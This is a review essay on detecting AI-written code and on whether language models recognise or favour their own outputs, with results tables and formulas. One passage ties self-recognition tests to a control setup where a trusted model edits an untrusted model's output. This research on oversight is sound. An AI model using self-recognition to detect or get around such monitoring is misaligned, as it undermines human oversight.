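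The trained classifiers did worse than guessing on the two-way task because most of its test code comes from programming languages or kinds of software that were absent from their training data. Averaged over the classifiers, macro-F1 was 0.63 on familiar contest code, 0.42 when only the language was new, and 0.20 when only the kind of software was new. Six of them scored exactly 18.02, the score a classifier would get by always choosing the rarer label. A judge that was never trained for the task has an advantage here because it doesn't depend on a narrow training set. It loses that advantage on the four-way task, where half of the test code comes from the same sources as the training code.

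The researchers also looked for programs that every classifier got wrong. On the two-way task, all the ones they found were human programs labeled as AI. They read these programs and found no consistent signs of a language model, such as wordy comments or odd names. Some were very short, such as a few lines that read a contest's name and a rating and print "yes" or "no". Another contained a ready-made class for comparing strings, of the kind contestants copy from one solution to the next. Orel and colleagues conclude that these programs fall outside the range of human code that the classifiers had learned to recognize. People write code in more varied ways than models do, so an unusual program may well be human.

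Ordinary coding habits can also count against someone. In the best trained classifier on the two-way task, names like `answer`, `result` and `index` pushed the verdict towards AI, while `li`, `cur` and `a1` pushed it towards human. The judges' checklist similarly lists consistent formatting and thorough handling of unusual inputs as signs of AI, and leftover experiments and quick fixes as signs of a person. A student who follows her lecturer's advice on clear names and tidy code therefore gives the judge reasons to think AI wrote it.

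### Measuring predictability instead of asking

A language model can also help detect machine-written code through the probabilities it computes as it processes the code, without classifying the code itself. *Zero-Shot Detection of LLM-Generated Code via Approximated Task Conditioning* (Ashkenazi, Brenner and colleagues, 2025) uses this approach.

At each point in a text, a language model assigns a probability to every token that could come next. Entropy measures how spread out those probabilities are. With two possible tokens, the entropy is 1 bit if they are equally likely and about 0.08 bits if one has a probability of 99%. Code that a model wrote should tend to have low entropy, because models mostly generate tokens to which other models also assign high probability.

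Entropy alone barely separates human from machine-written code. Ashkenazi and colleagues used Code Llama 7B to measure the entropy of human and machine-written solutions to Python problems from MBPP, a set of beginners' exercises, and APPS, which has harder problems and solutions by many different users. A random human program had higher entropy than a random machine-written one 56% of the time on MBPP and 52% on APPS, where guessing would give 50%. A model reading an unfamiliar program is uncertain about what the program is for, and this uncertainty outweighs any difference in how people and models write. If the model knows the task, most of the remaining uncertainty is about style.

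A teacher knows the task, but an analyst with a stray file does not, so the method has the model infer one:

1. Show the code to the model and ask it to write a task that would probably lead to similar code.
2. Put the inferred task $t$ in front of the code and have the model compute its probabilities for the whole text.
3. Average the entropy over the $m$ tokens of actual code. Comments stay in the text, where they work as extra hints about the task, but their own entropy doesn't count.
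4. Repeat with a few differently worded tasks, take the mean, and call the program machine-written if the result is below a chosen threshold.

For one inferred task, the score is

$$-\frac{1}{m}\sum_{k=1}^{m}\sum_{v} P(v \mid x_{<k}, t)\,\log P(v \mid x_{<k}, t),$$

where $v$ runs over all possible tokens and $x_{<k}$ is the text before the $k$-th code token.

With a single inferred task, the figures rose from 56% to 92% on MBPP and from 52% to 90% on APPS. The real task did little better, adding almost nothing on MBPP and about two points on APPS. Using four inferred tasks and a larger version of Code Llama raised both figures to about 94%. DetectCodeGPT, which had labelled everything machine-written in Djire's experiment, scored 77% on MBPP and 73% on APPS. It can evidently detect some difference between human and machine code, so a badly placed threshold may have caused part of its failure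 in Djire's experiment.

The results hold for seven generators, but the newest is GPT-4o mini, from 2024. When Ashkenazi and colleagues removed comments, the method still worked, losing about three points on APPS. They leave testing on edited or deliberately disguised code to future work. The method also does worse on short programs. This matters for beginners, who write short programs and often choose the most predictable solution because it's the one they were taught.

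Still, a numerical score has a practical advantage over a one-word answer because its user can decide how many false alarms to accept. When Ashkenazi and colleagues set the threshold to flag 10% of human programs, the method caught about 84% of machine-written ones. A teacher who finds 10% too high can choose a threshold that flags fewer human programs, but she will also catch fewer cheats. To find out which threshold flags 10% of the programs her own students write, she would need code she knows they wrote themselves.

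### A class of 100

Suppose 20 students in a class of 100 hand in a model's code as their own, and the teacher has a judge that catches 90% of machine-written programs and wrongly flags 10% of human-written ones. Ashkenazi and colleagues reached a slightly lower detection rate with the same rate of false alarms. The teacher's judge would flag 18 of the 20 students who cheated and 8 of the 80 who didn't, so nearly a third of the 26 flagged students would be innocent.

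The general formula, with $\pi$ for the share of students who cheat, $d$ for the detection rate and $f$ for the false-alarm rate, is

$$\text{share of flags that are correct} = \frac{\pi d}{\pi d + (1-\pi) f}.$$

Here the share of accusations that are correct is 0.18 / 0.26, or 69%. It was about a third in the earlier example, where the judge was equally accurate but only five assignments in 100 were machine-written. Lowering the false-alarm rate helps more than raising the detection rate. A judge that caught all 20 cheats but flagged 10% of honest students would be right in 71% of its accusations. If it caught 90% of the cheats and flagged 2% of honest students, it would be right in 92%.

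The teacher could wait for a second flag before accusing anyone, but the AICD Bench errors suggest that the judge's mistakes are not independent from one assignment to the next. An honest student whose natural style looks artificial to the judge will probably be flagged again. If the mistakes were independent, two flags in a row would be strong evidence, because they would pick out about 16 of the 20 cheats and fewer than one of the 80 honest students, on average. In the worst case, the same eight honest students are flagged every time, and the second flag makes the teacher more confident without adding any evidence.

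Some of the judges in Djire's experiment would wrongly flag far more students. If they misjudged honest students' programs as often as they misjudged the 18 human programs, Claude Sonnet 5 with the plain prompt would flag 40 of the 80 honest students, and Llama 3.1 would flag all 80.

### Code with two authors

The classroom example assumes that each student wrote either the whole program or none of it. Many students will have written most of the program and let an AI assistant fix a loop, and professional programmers work this way every day.

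Patterson and colleagues built their collection to resemble this kind of work. They had a model pick out self-contained pieces of a human-written Python file, replace each with a comment describing what the code did, and then write new code from the comments. They did this with three models and left about a tenth of the files untouched, so that a detector couldn't assume that every file contained machine-written code. The models wrote 17% of the 2.8 million lines in the finished collection. Each file was compared with the original, and unchanged lines were labeled as human, so the label is wrong wherever a model happened to rewrite a line exactly as it was.

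Patterson and colleagues tested two dedicated detectors on individual lines. DroidDetect flagged almost every line, so it found at least 98% of the machine-written ones, but only 2% to 27% of the lines it flagged were machine-written, depending on the model and the kind of line. AIGCode Detector may have been barely better than guessing, although its F1 is much higher and Patterson and colleagues conclude that it easily outperformed DroidDetect. Its scores look like a different kind of measurement from DroidDetect's. F1 for a single class always lies between precision and recall, but most of the F1 scores reported for AIGCode Detector are lower than both, which can happen if each figure is an average over the human and machine classes. Random guessing gets an average precision and recall of about 0.5, and AIGCode Detector's are between 0.49 and 0.57.

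Prompted judges did badly even at the easier task of labelling a whole file as hybrid. Gemini's best score on the four-way task in AICD Bench was 28.1, against 20.3 for guessing. The best trained classifier labelled 39% of hybrid programs correctly and called 58% of them AI. Some of those errors are debatable, because many of the hybrid programs are human code that Llama 3.3 rewrote from start to finish, so "AI" reasonably describes what wrote the final version. The same classifier also made clear mistakes, calling 15% of purely human programs hybrid and another 7% AI.

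SemEval, a yearly competition for language-processing systems, included hybrid and disguised code in one of its 2026 tasks. In *mcdok at SemEval-2026 Task 13*, Skurla, Macko and Simko describe how they adapted a detector for ordinary prose by training language models on code. Their results therefore don't show how well a model without that training can judge. Nobody appears to have published a test of how well a prompted model can identify the machine-written lines in a student's file, which a teacher who allows help with debugging but not with whole solutions would need to know.

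## Can a model recognise its own code or name another model's?

A language model normally has no memory of the programs it wrote in other conversations, so it can only recognise them by their style. Barkhordar and Thapa tested whether style is enough. The answer matters when models check code, because a model that recognised its own work might judge it too leniently.

Five models wrote solutions to Python problems from three public collections: 257 from MBPP, 164 from HumanEval, which also consists of short exercises, and 150 from DS-1000, which deal with tables of data. The five were OpenAI's GPT-5, Anthropic's Claude Haiku 4.5, Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash, xAI's Grok 4 Fast and the Chinese model DeepSeek-V3. Seven other models solved only the MBPP problems. Language models then judged the solutions zero-shot in four tasks:

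1. Say whether a single program is your own.
2. Pick your own program out of a pair.
3. Say which of two programs a named model wrote.
4. Choose the better of two programs, with no information about who wrote them.

For the pairs, Barkhordar and Thapa also scored seven rules that need no language model: choose the longer program, the shorter one, the one with or without a docstring, the one with or without type hints, or the one with more comment lines. A docstring is a description in quotation marks at the top of a function, and a type hint such as `n: int` states what kind of value a variable holds. If one of these rules identifies the author as often as the judge does, the judge's score is no evidence that it recognises anything more about the author's style. The researchers compared each judge with whichever rule did best on the same pairs, which gives the rules a slight advantage.

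### One program at a time

A third of the programs in the first task were the judge's own. The results for MBPP were as follows, in per cent.

| Judge | Said "yes" to its own code | Said "yes" to others' code | Balanced accuracy | Accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 0 | 0 | 50.0 | 61.2 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0 | 2 | 49.4 | 65.7 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 88 | 80 | 53.8 | 42.5 |
| Grok 4 Fast | 76 | 72 | 51.9 | 43.8 |
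| DeepSeek-V3 | 38 | 29 | 54.4 | 58.8 |

Claude has the highest accuracy in the table and the lowest balanced accuracy. It nearly always answered "no", and always answering "no" would have given an accuracy of 66.7%. Gemini has the lowest accuracy, but only because it usually answered "yes". Across all 15 combinations of model and collection, balanced accuracy was between 49% and 58%.

GPT-5 never answered "yes" for any of 1,668 programs. It declined to answer 5 to 10% of the time, usually explaining that it couldn't know whether it had written the code. That reply is sensible, especially as the prompt didn't mention that a third of the programs were its own. But these results don't show whether GPT-5 could distinguish its own code even slightly from the rest. Asking for a probability instead of a one-word answer might reveal a difference too small to change that answer.

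Grok and Gemini said "yes" to between 58% and 97% of programs, depending on the collection and the author. Grok did best on DS-1000, where it claimed 89% of its own programs and 72% of other models'. Of the 15 results, only this one and a smaller one for Grok on HumanEval remained statistically significant after correction for the number of tests. Even the larger difference has little practical value. If Grok wrote a third of the programs, a "yes" would raise the probability that it wrote a given program from 33% to about 38%.

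### Two programs side by side

A judge that must choose between two programs can't answer "no" every time. The next table shows how often each judge picked out its own MBPP solution and, in parentheses, how often that solution was the longer of the two. Some of Grok's matches are missing because the model was no longer available when the researchers added more pairs.

| Judge | Against Claude | Against DeepSeek | Against Gemini | Against GPT-5 | Against Grok |
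|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude | – | 83.9 (89) | 39.5 (25) | 31.5 (33) | – |
| DeepSeek | 31.0 (11) | – | 29.3 (5) | 30.5 (6) | – |
| Gemini | 64.1 (75) | 81.2 (95) | – | 50.0 (53) | – |
| GPT-5 | 47.9 (67) | 78.8 (94) | 45.1 (47) | – | 81.9 (97) |
| Grok | – | – | – | 41.1 (2) | – |

GPT-5 identified its own code in 81.9% of its pairs with Grok, but always choosing the longer program would have scored 97.5% on the same pairs, so the result doesn't show self-recognition. GPT-5's solutions averaged 18 lines and always had a docstring, while Grok's averaged 7 lines and only 17% had one. DeepSeek also wrote short programs, and it claimed its opponent's code as its own about 70% of the time, whoever the opponent was. If DeepSeek recognised its own style, writing short programs would not have pushed its score below the 50% expected by chance.

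The two numbers in each cell rise and fall together, with a correlation of 0.93. One can work out what to expect from a judge that ignores authorship and picks the longer program with probability $q$. If its own program is longer in a share $s$ of the pairs, its accuracy will be

$$qs + (1-q)(1-s).$$

As $s$ goes from 0 to 1, accuracy rises linearly from $1-q$ to $q$, with a slope of $2q-1$. Barkhordar and Thapa found a slope of 0.54, which corresponds to a judge that picks the longer program 77% of the time. In 12 of the 14 match-ups, the judges picked it between 59% and 87% of the time. The match-ups share judges and problems, so the correlation is only descriptive, but it stays at 0.90 or above when any one judge is left out.

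Length was not the only clue. In the two exceptions, GPT-5 had to tell its own code from Claude's or Gemini's, which is documented just as thoroughly, and it picked the longer program only about half the time. When Claude was compared with GPT-5, it was right 50.6% of the time when its own program was longer and 22.2% when it was shorter. If Claude had used length alone, those figures would add up to about 100%. They add up to 73%, so something else made Claude favour GPT-5's code, perhaps its type hints, which Claude's solutions often lacked. The judges may have been claiming whichever program they rated as better, an explanation that other researchers have tested directly.

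Some answers depended on the order of the programs. When the researchers repeated Claude's test against GPT-5 six months later, Claude's accuracy was again 31.5%. Claude chose the same program as before in 97.5% of the pairs shown in the original order, but in only about three quarters of those shown in reverse order. Rewording the prompt changed accuracy by up to ten points, but scores that had been below 50% stayed below 50%.

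### Telling the styles apart and swapping the names

In the third task, the judge saw two programs and the names of the two models that wrote them, and had to say which program one of those models had written. GPT-5.3-Codex, an OpenAI model for programming, had to pick out Claude Opus 4.6's program in 257 pairs where Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite had written the other. It was right 20 times (7.8%), while guessing would have been right about 128 times.

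GPT-5.3-Codex, like Gemini 3 Flash in Djire's experiment, could tell the programs apart but swapped the labels. The distinction was easy because only 7 of Opus's 257 solutions had a docstring, while nearly all of Gemini's did. GPT-5.3-Codex evidently detected this difference but attributed the documented program to Claude.

Barkhordar and Thapa also asked GPT-5.3-Codex to pick out Gemini's program in each pair. On 68% of the pairs it swapped the names, attributing Gemini's program to Opus and Opus's to Gemini. It got both right on 7%. On almost all the rest, it picked the documented program for both questions. A judge guessing at random would swap the names on about 25% of the pairs and get both right on another 25%.

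This reversed attribution may come from a stereotype about the model family. Claude Haiku 4.5 put a docstring in 98% of its MBPP solutions, so a judge that associates docstrings with Claude models would be right about Haiku and wrong about Opus. Some of the models were released too shortly before the judges, or after them, for the judges to have learned those models' individual habits, so the judges could use only what they had learned about the family name.

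The other possible explanation is that GPT-5.3-Codex rates Opus as the stronger model and documented code as better code, and so attributes documented code to Opus. The model's name has to play a part, because a judge that simply favoured documented code would pick the same program whichever model the question named. Gemini 2.5 Flash mostly did this when it judged Claude Haiku against DeepSeek, picking the same program for both names on 90% of the pairs. It was right 77.3% of the time when asked about Claude and 27.1% when asked about DeepSeek, so the higher figure alone would greatly overstate its ability to tell them apart.

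The experiment can't distinguish between these explanations, because both predict that the judge will attribute the documented program to Opus. A better test would pair a small Claude model with a stronger model from a family that the judge doesn't associate with docstrings, on problems where only one of the two programs has a docstring. The judge would attribute the documented program to Claude if it relied on the stereotype, and to the stronger model if it relied on the belief about quality.

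Judges sometimes correctly identified which program a named model had written. Grok-Code-Fast-1 identified Claude Haiku's code 81.6% of the time when it was paired with DeepSeek's, but the simple rule of choosing the longer program would have scored 89.0%. Only GPT-5.3-Codex clearly beat every such rule. It identified Gemini 2.5 Flash's code 76.2% of the time when it was paired with GPT-5's, while the best rule scored 52.9%. GPT-5.3-Codex is closely related to GPT-5, so it may have recognised GPT-5's style and ruled that program out.

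GPT-5 did slightly better than the rules on programs by Mistral's model Codestral because some of them contained a stray line. Codestral had ended 79 of its 257 answers with the wrong formatting marker, which left that line in the code. GPT-5 judged 72.2% of those programs correctly and exactly 50% of the others.

### The order of the names

An early version of the prompt for this task gave the judges a much simpler clue. Barkhordar and Thapa had shuffled the two programs, but the prompt always listed the authors' names in the same order as the programs, even though it described the order as random. A judge could therefore match names to programs without reading any code.

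In eight of the ten runs with this prompt, accuracy was between 86% and 99%. The clue may not account for all of this, because most of the runs compared Claude Haiku with DeepSeek, and the rule about length scores 89% on that pair. No judge tried that pair with both versions of the prompt, so the size of the clue's effect is unknown, though GPT-5's 98.8% is hard to explain without it.

Accuracy in the other two runs was 31.0% and 19.9%. Barkhordar and Thapa suggest that these judges used the order of the names backwards. But the same judges scored 92.9% and 92.1% when the question named the other model in the pair, so they would have had to use the order correctly for one name and backwards for the other. More likely, they mostly ignored the order and picked the longer program whichever model the question named, as Gemini did. Both low scores came from questions about DeepSeek, which wrote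 the shorter programs.

The researchers set aside all ten runs and repeated the task, randomising the order of the names separately from the order of the programs. Every result in the previous section comes from the corrected prompt.

### Removing the style

If the judges rely on docstrings, comments and names, removing those should remove their ability to tell authors apart. Barkhordar and Thapa wrote a program that normalizes code, which means rewriting it without such surface cues while keeping its behaviour. Take this function, which counts the long words in a text:

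```python
def count_long_words(text: str, min_length: int) -> int:
    """Count the words with at least min_length letters."""
    total = 0
    for word in text.split():
        # Ignore punctuation around the word
        cleaned = word.strip(".,;:!?")
        if len(cleaned) >= min_length:
            total += 1
    return total
```

Normalization deletes the docstring, the comment and the type hints. It renames the parameters and local variables in order, then prints the code again from its syntax tree, so that everyone's spacing and quotation marks are the same:

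```python
def count_long_words(v0, v1):
    v2 = 0
    for v3 in v0.split():
        v4 = v3.strip('.,;:!?')
        if len(v4) >= v1:
            v2 += 1
    return v2
```

The function keeps its name because the tests call it by that name. Text inside quotation marks, such as the list of punctuation, also stays the same. The structure of the code doesn't change either, so a model that had used a single line with Python's `sum` to count the words would still have a shorter program after normalization.

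After normalization, every program from the five main models passed or failed the tests exactly as before. Many pairs became identical, up to a third for some models, and the researchers excluded them. They then measured 12 of the earlier results again on the normalized code. The table shows six of these as percentages of correct answers.

| Judge | Program to find | Original code | Normalized code |
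|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | Its own, against Grok's | 81.9 | 45.2 |
| DeepSeek-V3 | Its own, against GPT-5's | 30.5 | 56.5 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | Its own, against GPT-5's | 31.5 | 35.3 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | Claude Haiku's, against DeepSeek's | 77.3 | 46.5 |
| GPT-5.3-Codex | Gemini 2.5's, against GPT-5's | 76.2 | 57.8 |
| GPT-5.3-Codex | Claude Opus's, against Gemini 3.1's | 7.8 | 39.2 |

Ten of the twelve results ended up between 43.6% and 57.8%, and none of these differed significantly from chance after correction for multiple tests. High scores fell and low scores rose, as expected if surface cues had caused both. Because the samples were small, the tests could have missed a real effect of up to 14 points.

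The two exceptions were Claude looking for its own code and GPT-5.3-Codex looking for Opus's. Both judges still tended to choose the longer program, and normalization doesn't make programs equally long. GPT-5's programs were still usually longer than Grok's, so choosing the longer one would have scored 85%, but GPT-5 scored 45%. It had apparently been relying on the documentation that made its programs long rather than on length itself.

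Normalized code still contains plenty of evidence about who wrote it. Barkhordar and Thapa trained a simple classifier on runs of two to five characters and tested it on problems not used in training. It distinguished GPT-5's normalized code from that of each of the other four main models 93 to 96% of the time. Its accuracy for the remaining pairs was 58 to 83%.

The comparison with the judges is uneven because the classifier learned from about 200 labelled programs by each model, while the judges had no examples. A few-shot prompt with several normalized programs by each model would be a fairer test. It would help show whether the judges can't detect the remaining differences or can detect them but can't match them to the right model.

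### Does a model prefer its own code?

A judge could favour its own programs without recognising them, for example because it writes the kind of code it rates highly. In the fourth task, the judges compared two programs without being told who wrote them. Their instructions were to judge correctness first and to ignore comments, docstrings and formatting unless these affected correctness.

A model may prefer its own programs because they are better, so counting how often it does so can overstate its bias. Barkhordar and Thapa therefore had both models judge the same pairs of programs, with one program from each model. Let $p_X$ be the share of pairs in which model X picks its own program, and $p_Y$ the share in which model Y picks X's program. If the models agree on which programs are better, the two shares are equal. The difference $p_X - p_Y$ measures the two models' combined self-preference.

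To find out which of the two is responsible, the researchers added a neutral judge, Z, which had written neither program:

$$p_X - p_Y = (p_X - p_Z) + (p_Z - p_Y).$$

The first part measures how much more X likes its own code than Z does. The second does the same for Y. Here is how often the first model's program won, in per cent:

| Programs by | First model judges | Neutral model judges | Second model judges |
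|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku and DeepSeek | 75.2 | 63.4 (Gemini) | 64.2 |
| Claude Haiku and Gemini | 45.9 | 48.6 (DeepSeek) | 45.9 |
| Gemini and DeepSeek | 66.3 | 72.9 (Claude) | 61.6 |
| GPT-5 and DeepSeek | 70.9 | 70.5 (Gemini) | 71.8 |

Only the first row shows a clear self-preference. The combined effect is 11 points, and on this split all of it comes from Claude. The effect was just as large on pairs in which both programs passed the tests or both failed, so Claude wasn't simply better at spotting correct code. When only one program had a docstring, Claude chose it 84% of the time, despite the instruction to ignore docstrings. It did so 76% of the time even when judging Gemini's code against DeepSeek's.

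The third row shows why the split needs careful interpretation. Claude is a poor standard of neutrality here because it favours documented programs even more than Gemini does. Compared with Claude, Gemini seems to disfavour its own code by 6.6 points and DeepSeek seems to favour its own by 11.3. The combined effect, which doesn't depend on the neutral judge, is only 4.7 points in this row and is not statistically significant.

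On normalised code, Claude's preference for its own programs over DeepSeek's disappeared. Claude chose its own programs 47.8% of the time, and the neutral judge chose them 48.9% of the time. This agrees with the evidence that Claude favours docstrings rather than its own work. The test did not measure the effect of a label telling the judge that the code is its own, which could make the judge more lenient even if it doesn't recognise the code.

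All these experiments used short Python programs. The main models' MBPP solutions averaged 7 to 20 lines, far less than a professional reviewer normally sees, and longer files might offer more clues. GPT-5 was the only flagship model asked to recognise its own code. The others were small, fast or older, and stronger models might do better. The prompts for HumanEval and DS-1000 also asked for comments or docstrings and clear names, which made the models' styles more alike. The results are good evidence that these models can't recognise their own code of this kind, but they don't show how the best current models would do on a whole project.

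### Training a classifier

Training a classifier on model-written code gives much better results than asking a model who wrote it. Bisztray, Gruschka and colleagues (2025), in *I Know Which LLM Wrote Your Code Last Summer*, collected 32,000 C programs written by eight models. Their best classifier distinguished GPT-4.1 from GPT-4o with 97.6% accuracy and chose among five models from different companies with 95.4% accuracy. Removing comments from the code lowered another classifier's accuracy on the five models from 92.7% to 85.5%.

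Their test may have been easier than it looks because the 4,000 tasks came from only 300 templates, such as sorting a list of a given size, so each model answered every template about 13 times. The researchers don't report keeping all versions of a template together when they split the data into training and test sets, so the classifier could have learned a model's usual answer to a particular exercise instead of its general style. They also tried the classifier on new prompts, but they report its confidence rather than its accuracy over a stated number of programs.

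In *The Hidden DNA of LLM-Generated JavaScript*, Tihanyi, Cherif and colleagues (2025) trained classifiers on 50,000 programs by 20 models, then tested one of them on 500 programs for new tasks. Its accuracy at choosing among five models dropped by only one or two percentage points. When choosing among all 20 models, where guessing would score 5%, their own classifier was right 86% of the time in the main comparison and 84% of the time after a tool had shortened the names in the code. Comments and names therefore help to identify a model, but a trained classifier can do well without them.

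Another way to find a model's style is to subtract everything that depends on the task. Guo, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *Code Fingerprints*, had four models solve the same 2,869 LeetCode problems in four languages, both with and without comments. One neural network turns each program into a list of 768 numbers, $h$. A second network learns to extract from $h$ a part, $h_{\text{task}}$, that is as similar as possible for different models' solutions to the same problem. The classifier then uses only the remainder,

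$$h_{\text{style}} = h - h_{\text{task}}.$$

By Barkhordar and Thapa's account, this method reached an F1 of about 93% on code without comments.

All three classifiers choose from a fixed list, so they will always name the wrong model if the true one is missing. GPT-4o usually made the same mistake with human suspects. AICD Bench comes closer to real conditions by including code from models that the classifiers did not see in training, though these models always belong to a known family. Orel and colleagues conclude from the benchmark as a whole that detectors are still far from usable in practice.

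### Testing a large set of programs

Someone who suspects one particular model can avoid both prompting and training. In *Zero-Shot Attribution for Large Language Models* (2025), Canonne, Pote and Sarkar describe Anubis, a tool that uses the probabilities a model assigns to each token. It doesn't judge a single program. It takes a large set of solutions to the same problem and decides whether most of them or very few of them came from the suspected model:

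1. Have the suspected model write as many new solutions as there are in the set.
2. Compute the probability $P(x)$ that the model would write each program $x$, by multiplying the probabilities of its tokens. Sort the programs from both sets into buckets, where bucket $j$ holds those with $2^{-j} < P(x) \le 2^{-j+1}$.
3. Compare how the two sets are spread over the buckets. If the difference is large, reject the suspected model.
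4. Within each bucket, compare how often each exact program appears in the two sets. This catches a model that writes different programs which happen to be about as probable.

If both comparisons find only small differences, Anubis concludes that the suspected model wrote most of the set.

Canonne and colleagues tested the method on two small models, DeepSeek-Coder and CodeGemma, by mixing their code with code from a third model, Stable Code. They used 2,000 solutions to each of the 164 HumanEval problems. The task was to tell whether the suspected model had written a large or a small share of a set of solutions, and it was easiest when the two shares were far apart, such as at least 90% versus at most 20%. When the gap was 70 percentage points or more, a random set with the large share scored higher than a random set with the small share more than 90% of the time. The researchers report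 at least 80% reliability with 1,000 solutions. An older method, DetectGPT, did much worse, but it was designed for single texts, and Canonne and colleagues had to combine its scores to use it on a set.

Anubis needs access to the suspected model's probabilities, which some companies don't provide. It also needs far more code than a teacher or a malware analyst is likely to have. It would suit a customer who pays for one model and suspects the supplier is running a cheaper one. The customer could send the same problem 2,000 times and test the answers, if they can also run the model they paid for themselves.

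## Why models claim the better answer as their own

Judges in the last section tended to claim the longer, better-documented program as their own, whoever had written it. Two earlier papers disagreed about whether models can recognise their own prose. *LLM Evaluators Recognize and Favor Their Own Generations* (Panickssery, Bowman and Feng, 2024) reported that they can. *Self-Recognition in Language Models* (Davidson, Surkov and colleagues, 2024) found no general ability to do so, and the models it tested seemed to pick whichever answer they thought was best.

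### Summaries and security questions

Panickssery and colleagues had GPT-4, GPT-3.5 and Llama 2 7B summarise 2,000 news articles. They showed each model two summaries and asked which one it had written. GPT-4 was right 73.5% of the time when the other summary came from one of the other two models or a human writer. Llama 2 could not tell its summaries from those of GPT-3.5 or GPT-4, and GPT-3.5 struggled to tell its own from GPT-4's. When the models were shown one summary at a time, only GPT-4 did noticeably better than chance, and it hardly ever identified a summary as its own.

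Davidson and colleagues adapted the security questions that banks ask to check a caller's identity. They had ten models write questions whose answers were supposed to reveal which model had replied. Each model answered the questions, then tried to pick its own answer from a group of two, three or five. Claude 3 Opus chose its own answer over GPT-3.5's 88% of the time, but GPT-3.5 chose its own over Claude's only 30% of the time. Weaker models generally claimed stronger models' answers as their own. The pattern was much the same when the researchers asked the models which answer they preferred instead of which they had written.

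This also explains why Llama 2 failed against stronger models in the first experiment, where Panickssery and colleagues had not controlled for the quality of the summaries. But it doesn't explain everything, because the success rates of Claude and GPT-3.5 add up to 118%. If the two models always agreed on the better answer and claimed it as their own, exactly one of them would be right about each pair, and their success rates would add up to 100%.

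Some of the excess may come from verbal habits. In answers of up to 100 words, Claude 3 Opus was right 82% of the time when its answer began with a preamble, and 62% when it had neither a preamble nor a refusal. For Llama 3 70B, which tended to compliment the user, the figures were 80% and 67%. *Strangers to Themselves* (2026) still calls the question contested, citing a 2025 test in which ten models rarely beat chance.

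### Four ways of asking

St. Amand, Canavan and colleagues (2026) argue in *Self-Generated Text Recognition* that researchers got different results partly because they asked in different ways. Their study covered up to 21 models from seven companies. Three of the models were tested both with and without written reasoning, which makes 24 judges.

The models first responded to 250 prompts. Fifty came from BigCodeBench, a set of programming tasks that require several software libraries. One task is to split a data file into smaller files and shuffle the lines in each. The other prompts were 50 articles to summarise, 100 everyday chatbot requests and 50 questions on sensitive topics.

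The judges saw either a pair of answers or a single one. In one version, the answers were in the user's message, and the prompt said that the model had written one of them in another conversation. In the other, they appeared as the model's own earlier turns, and the prompt said that another model's text had replaced one of them. The second version resembles a safety measure in which a trusted model edits an untrusted model's output, so developers have a reason to find out whether the untrusted model would notice the edits.

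For single answers, St. Amand and colleagues used balanced accuracy. They told the judge that half of the answers were its own, whereas Barkhordar and Thapa did not tell theirs the share.

### Do the claims follow quality?

To estimate quality, St. Amand and colleagues used ratings from Arena, a website where people compare two models' answers and vote for the better one. Arena uses Elo ratings, as chess does. A model whose rating is $d$ points higher than its opponent's should win a share of the votes equal to

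$$\frac{1}{1+10^{-d/400}}.$$

With a 100-point advantage, that is 64%.

If judges claim the better answer, they should do well against lower-rated models and badly against higher-rated ones, and this is what happened. In pairs shown as the user's material, each 100 points of rating advantage added about 15 percentage points of accuracy. On the average fitted line, a judge rated 200 points above the other model is right about 90% of the time, and one rated 200 points below is right about 30%. A judge that simply couldn't recognise its own work would score 50% in both cases.

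The 15 points are close to the 14 that the formula gives for human votes, so the average judge behaved roughly as if it claimed the answer an Arena voter would choose. The match may be partly luck, since Arena voters judged answers to different prompts.

| How the judge saw the answers | Accuracy gained per 100 rating points | Accuracy at equal ratings | Judges above 50% at equal ratings |
|---|---|---|---|
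| Pair, in the user's message | 15 points | 59.9% | 21 of 23 |
| Single, in the user's message | 6 points | 54.0% | 19 of 23 |
| Pair, as the model's earlier turns | 9 points | 59.8% | 12 of 12 |
| Single, as the model's earlier turn | 5 points | 51.6% | 8 of 12 |

The gains for single answers are smaller partly because of the scoring. Half the score comes from the judge's own answers, which are the same for every opponent, so the rating gap can affect only the other half.

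The rating gap accounts for 23 to 34% of the variation in a judge's accuracy within one kind of task (an R² of 0.23 to 0.34), depending on the format. But a rating covers a model's answers in general, and a highly rated model can still write a bad program. St. Amand and colleagues therefore also asked the judges which answer in each pair was better. The more often a judge preferred its own answers, the more often it claimed them. The R² for this relationship was between 0.61 and 0.89 for the four kinds of task, and between 0.04 and 0.75 for single answers.

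These are comparisons between averages. A judge could claim 70% of its own answers and prefer 70% of them without the two sets being the same. Panickssery and colleagues had checked individual summaries and found a moderate link. GPT-3.5's confidence that it had written a summary had a rank correlation of about 0.4 with its confidence that the summary was better.

Panickssery and colleagues hypothesised the reverse, that models prefer an answer because they recognise it as their own. That may happen in some cases, but it can't explain why weaker models claim the work of stronger ones.

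### Above chance at equal ratings

Quality doesn't account for all of the judges' success. St. Amand and colleagues fitted the line

$$\text{accuracy} = \alpha_j + \beta d,$$

where $\alpha_j$ is the accuracy of judge $j$ against a model with the same rating. In the first row of the table, 21 of 23 judges have an $\alpha_j$ above 50%, and for 17 of them the whole 95% interval is above it. Qwen 3.0 80B has the highest, at 78.4%, and Gemini 2.0 Flash Lite the lowest, at 44.0%. The average of 59.9% means that two typical judges' success rates add up to about 120%, much like the 118% for Claude 3 Opus and GPT-3.5.

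A judge can beat chance at equal ratings without any self-knowledge. Arena ratings reflect the average voter's preferences, which may differ from a model's. The training that teaches a model to write bulleted lists probably also teaches it to rate them highly. If such a model claimed the answers it preferred, it would claim its own more often than the ratings predict. Claude Haiku's preference for docstrings would have the same effect, since its own programs nearly always had them. St. Amand and colleagues did not control for the length or correctness of the answers, or identify the features that the judges relied on.

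Measurements inside the models give better evidence of self-knowledge. Asvin G. and Lindsey (2026), in *From Simulation to Enaction*, measured how uncertain five models were about the next token (their entropy) as they read various answers. Each model was less uncertain on its own text than on any other model's. The effect was essentially absent in models with about 2 billion parameters and largest in those with about 70 billion. So these models process their own text differently, at least for simple prompts and models well behind the current best.

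It is unclear whether judges use that difference when asked who wrote an answer. In the main test of the difference, on Llama 3.1 70B, it was largest when the text appeared as the model's own turn. If judges relied on it, St. Amand and colleagues' second version should have been easier. For the 12 judges that took both versions, average accuracy at equal ratings rose from about 58% to 60% for pairs but fell from 54% to 52% for single answers. Claude Sonnet 4.5 rose from 54% to 69% on pairs and Claude Opus 4.1 from 72% to 79%, but neither improved on single answers, where the judge can't compare two styles.

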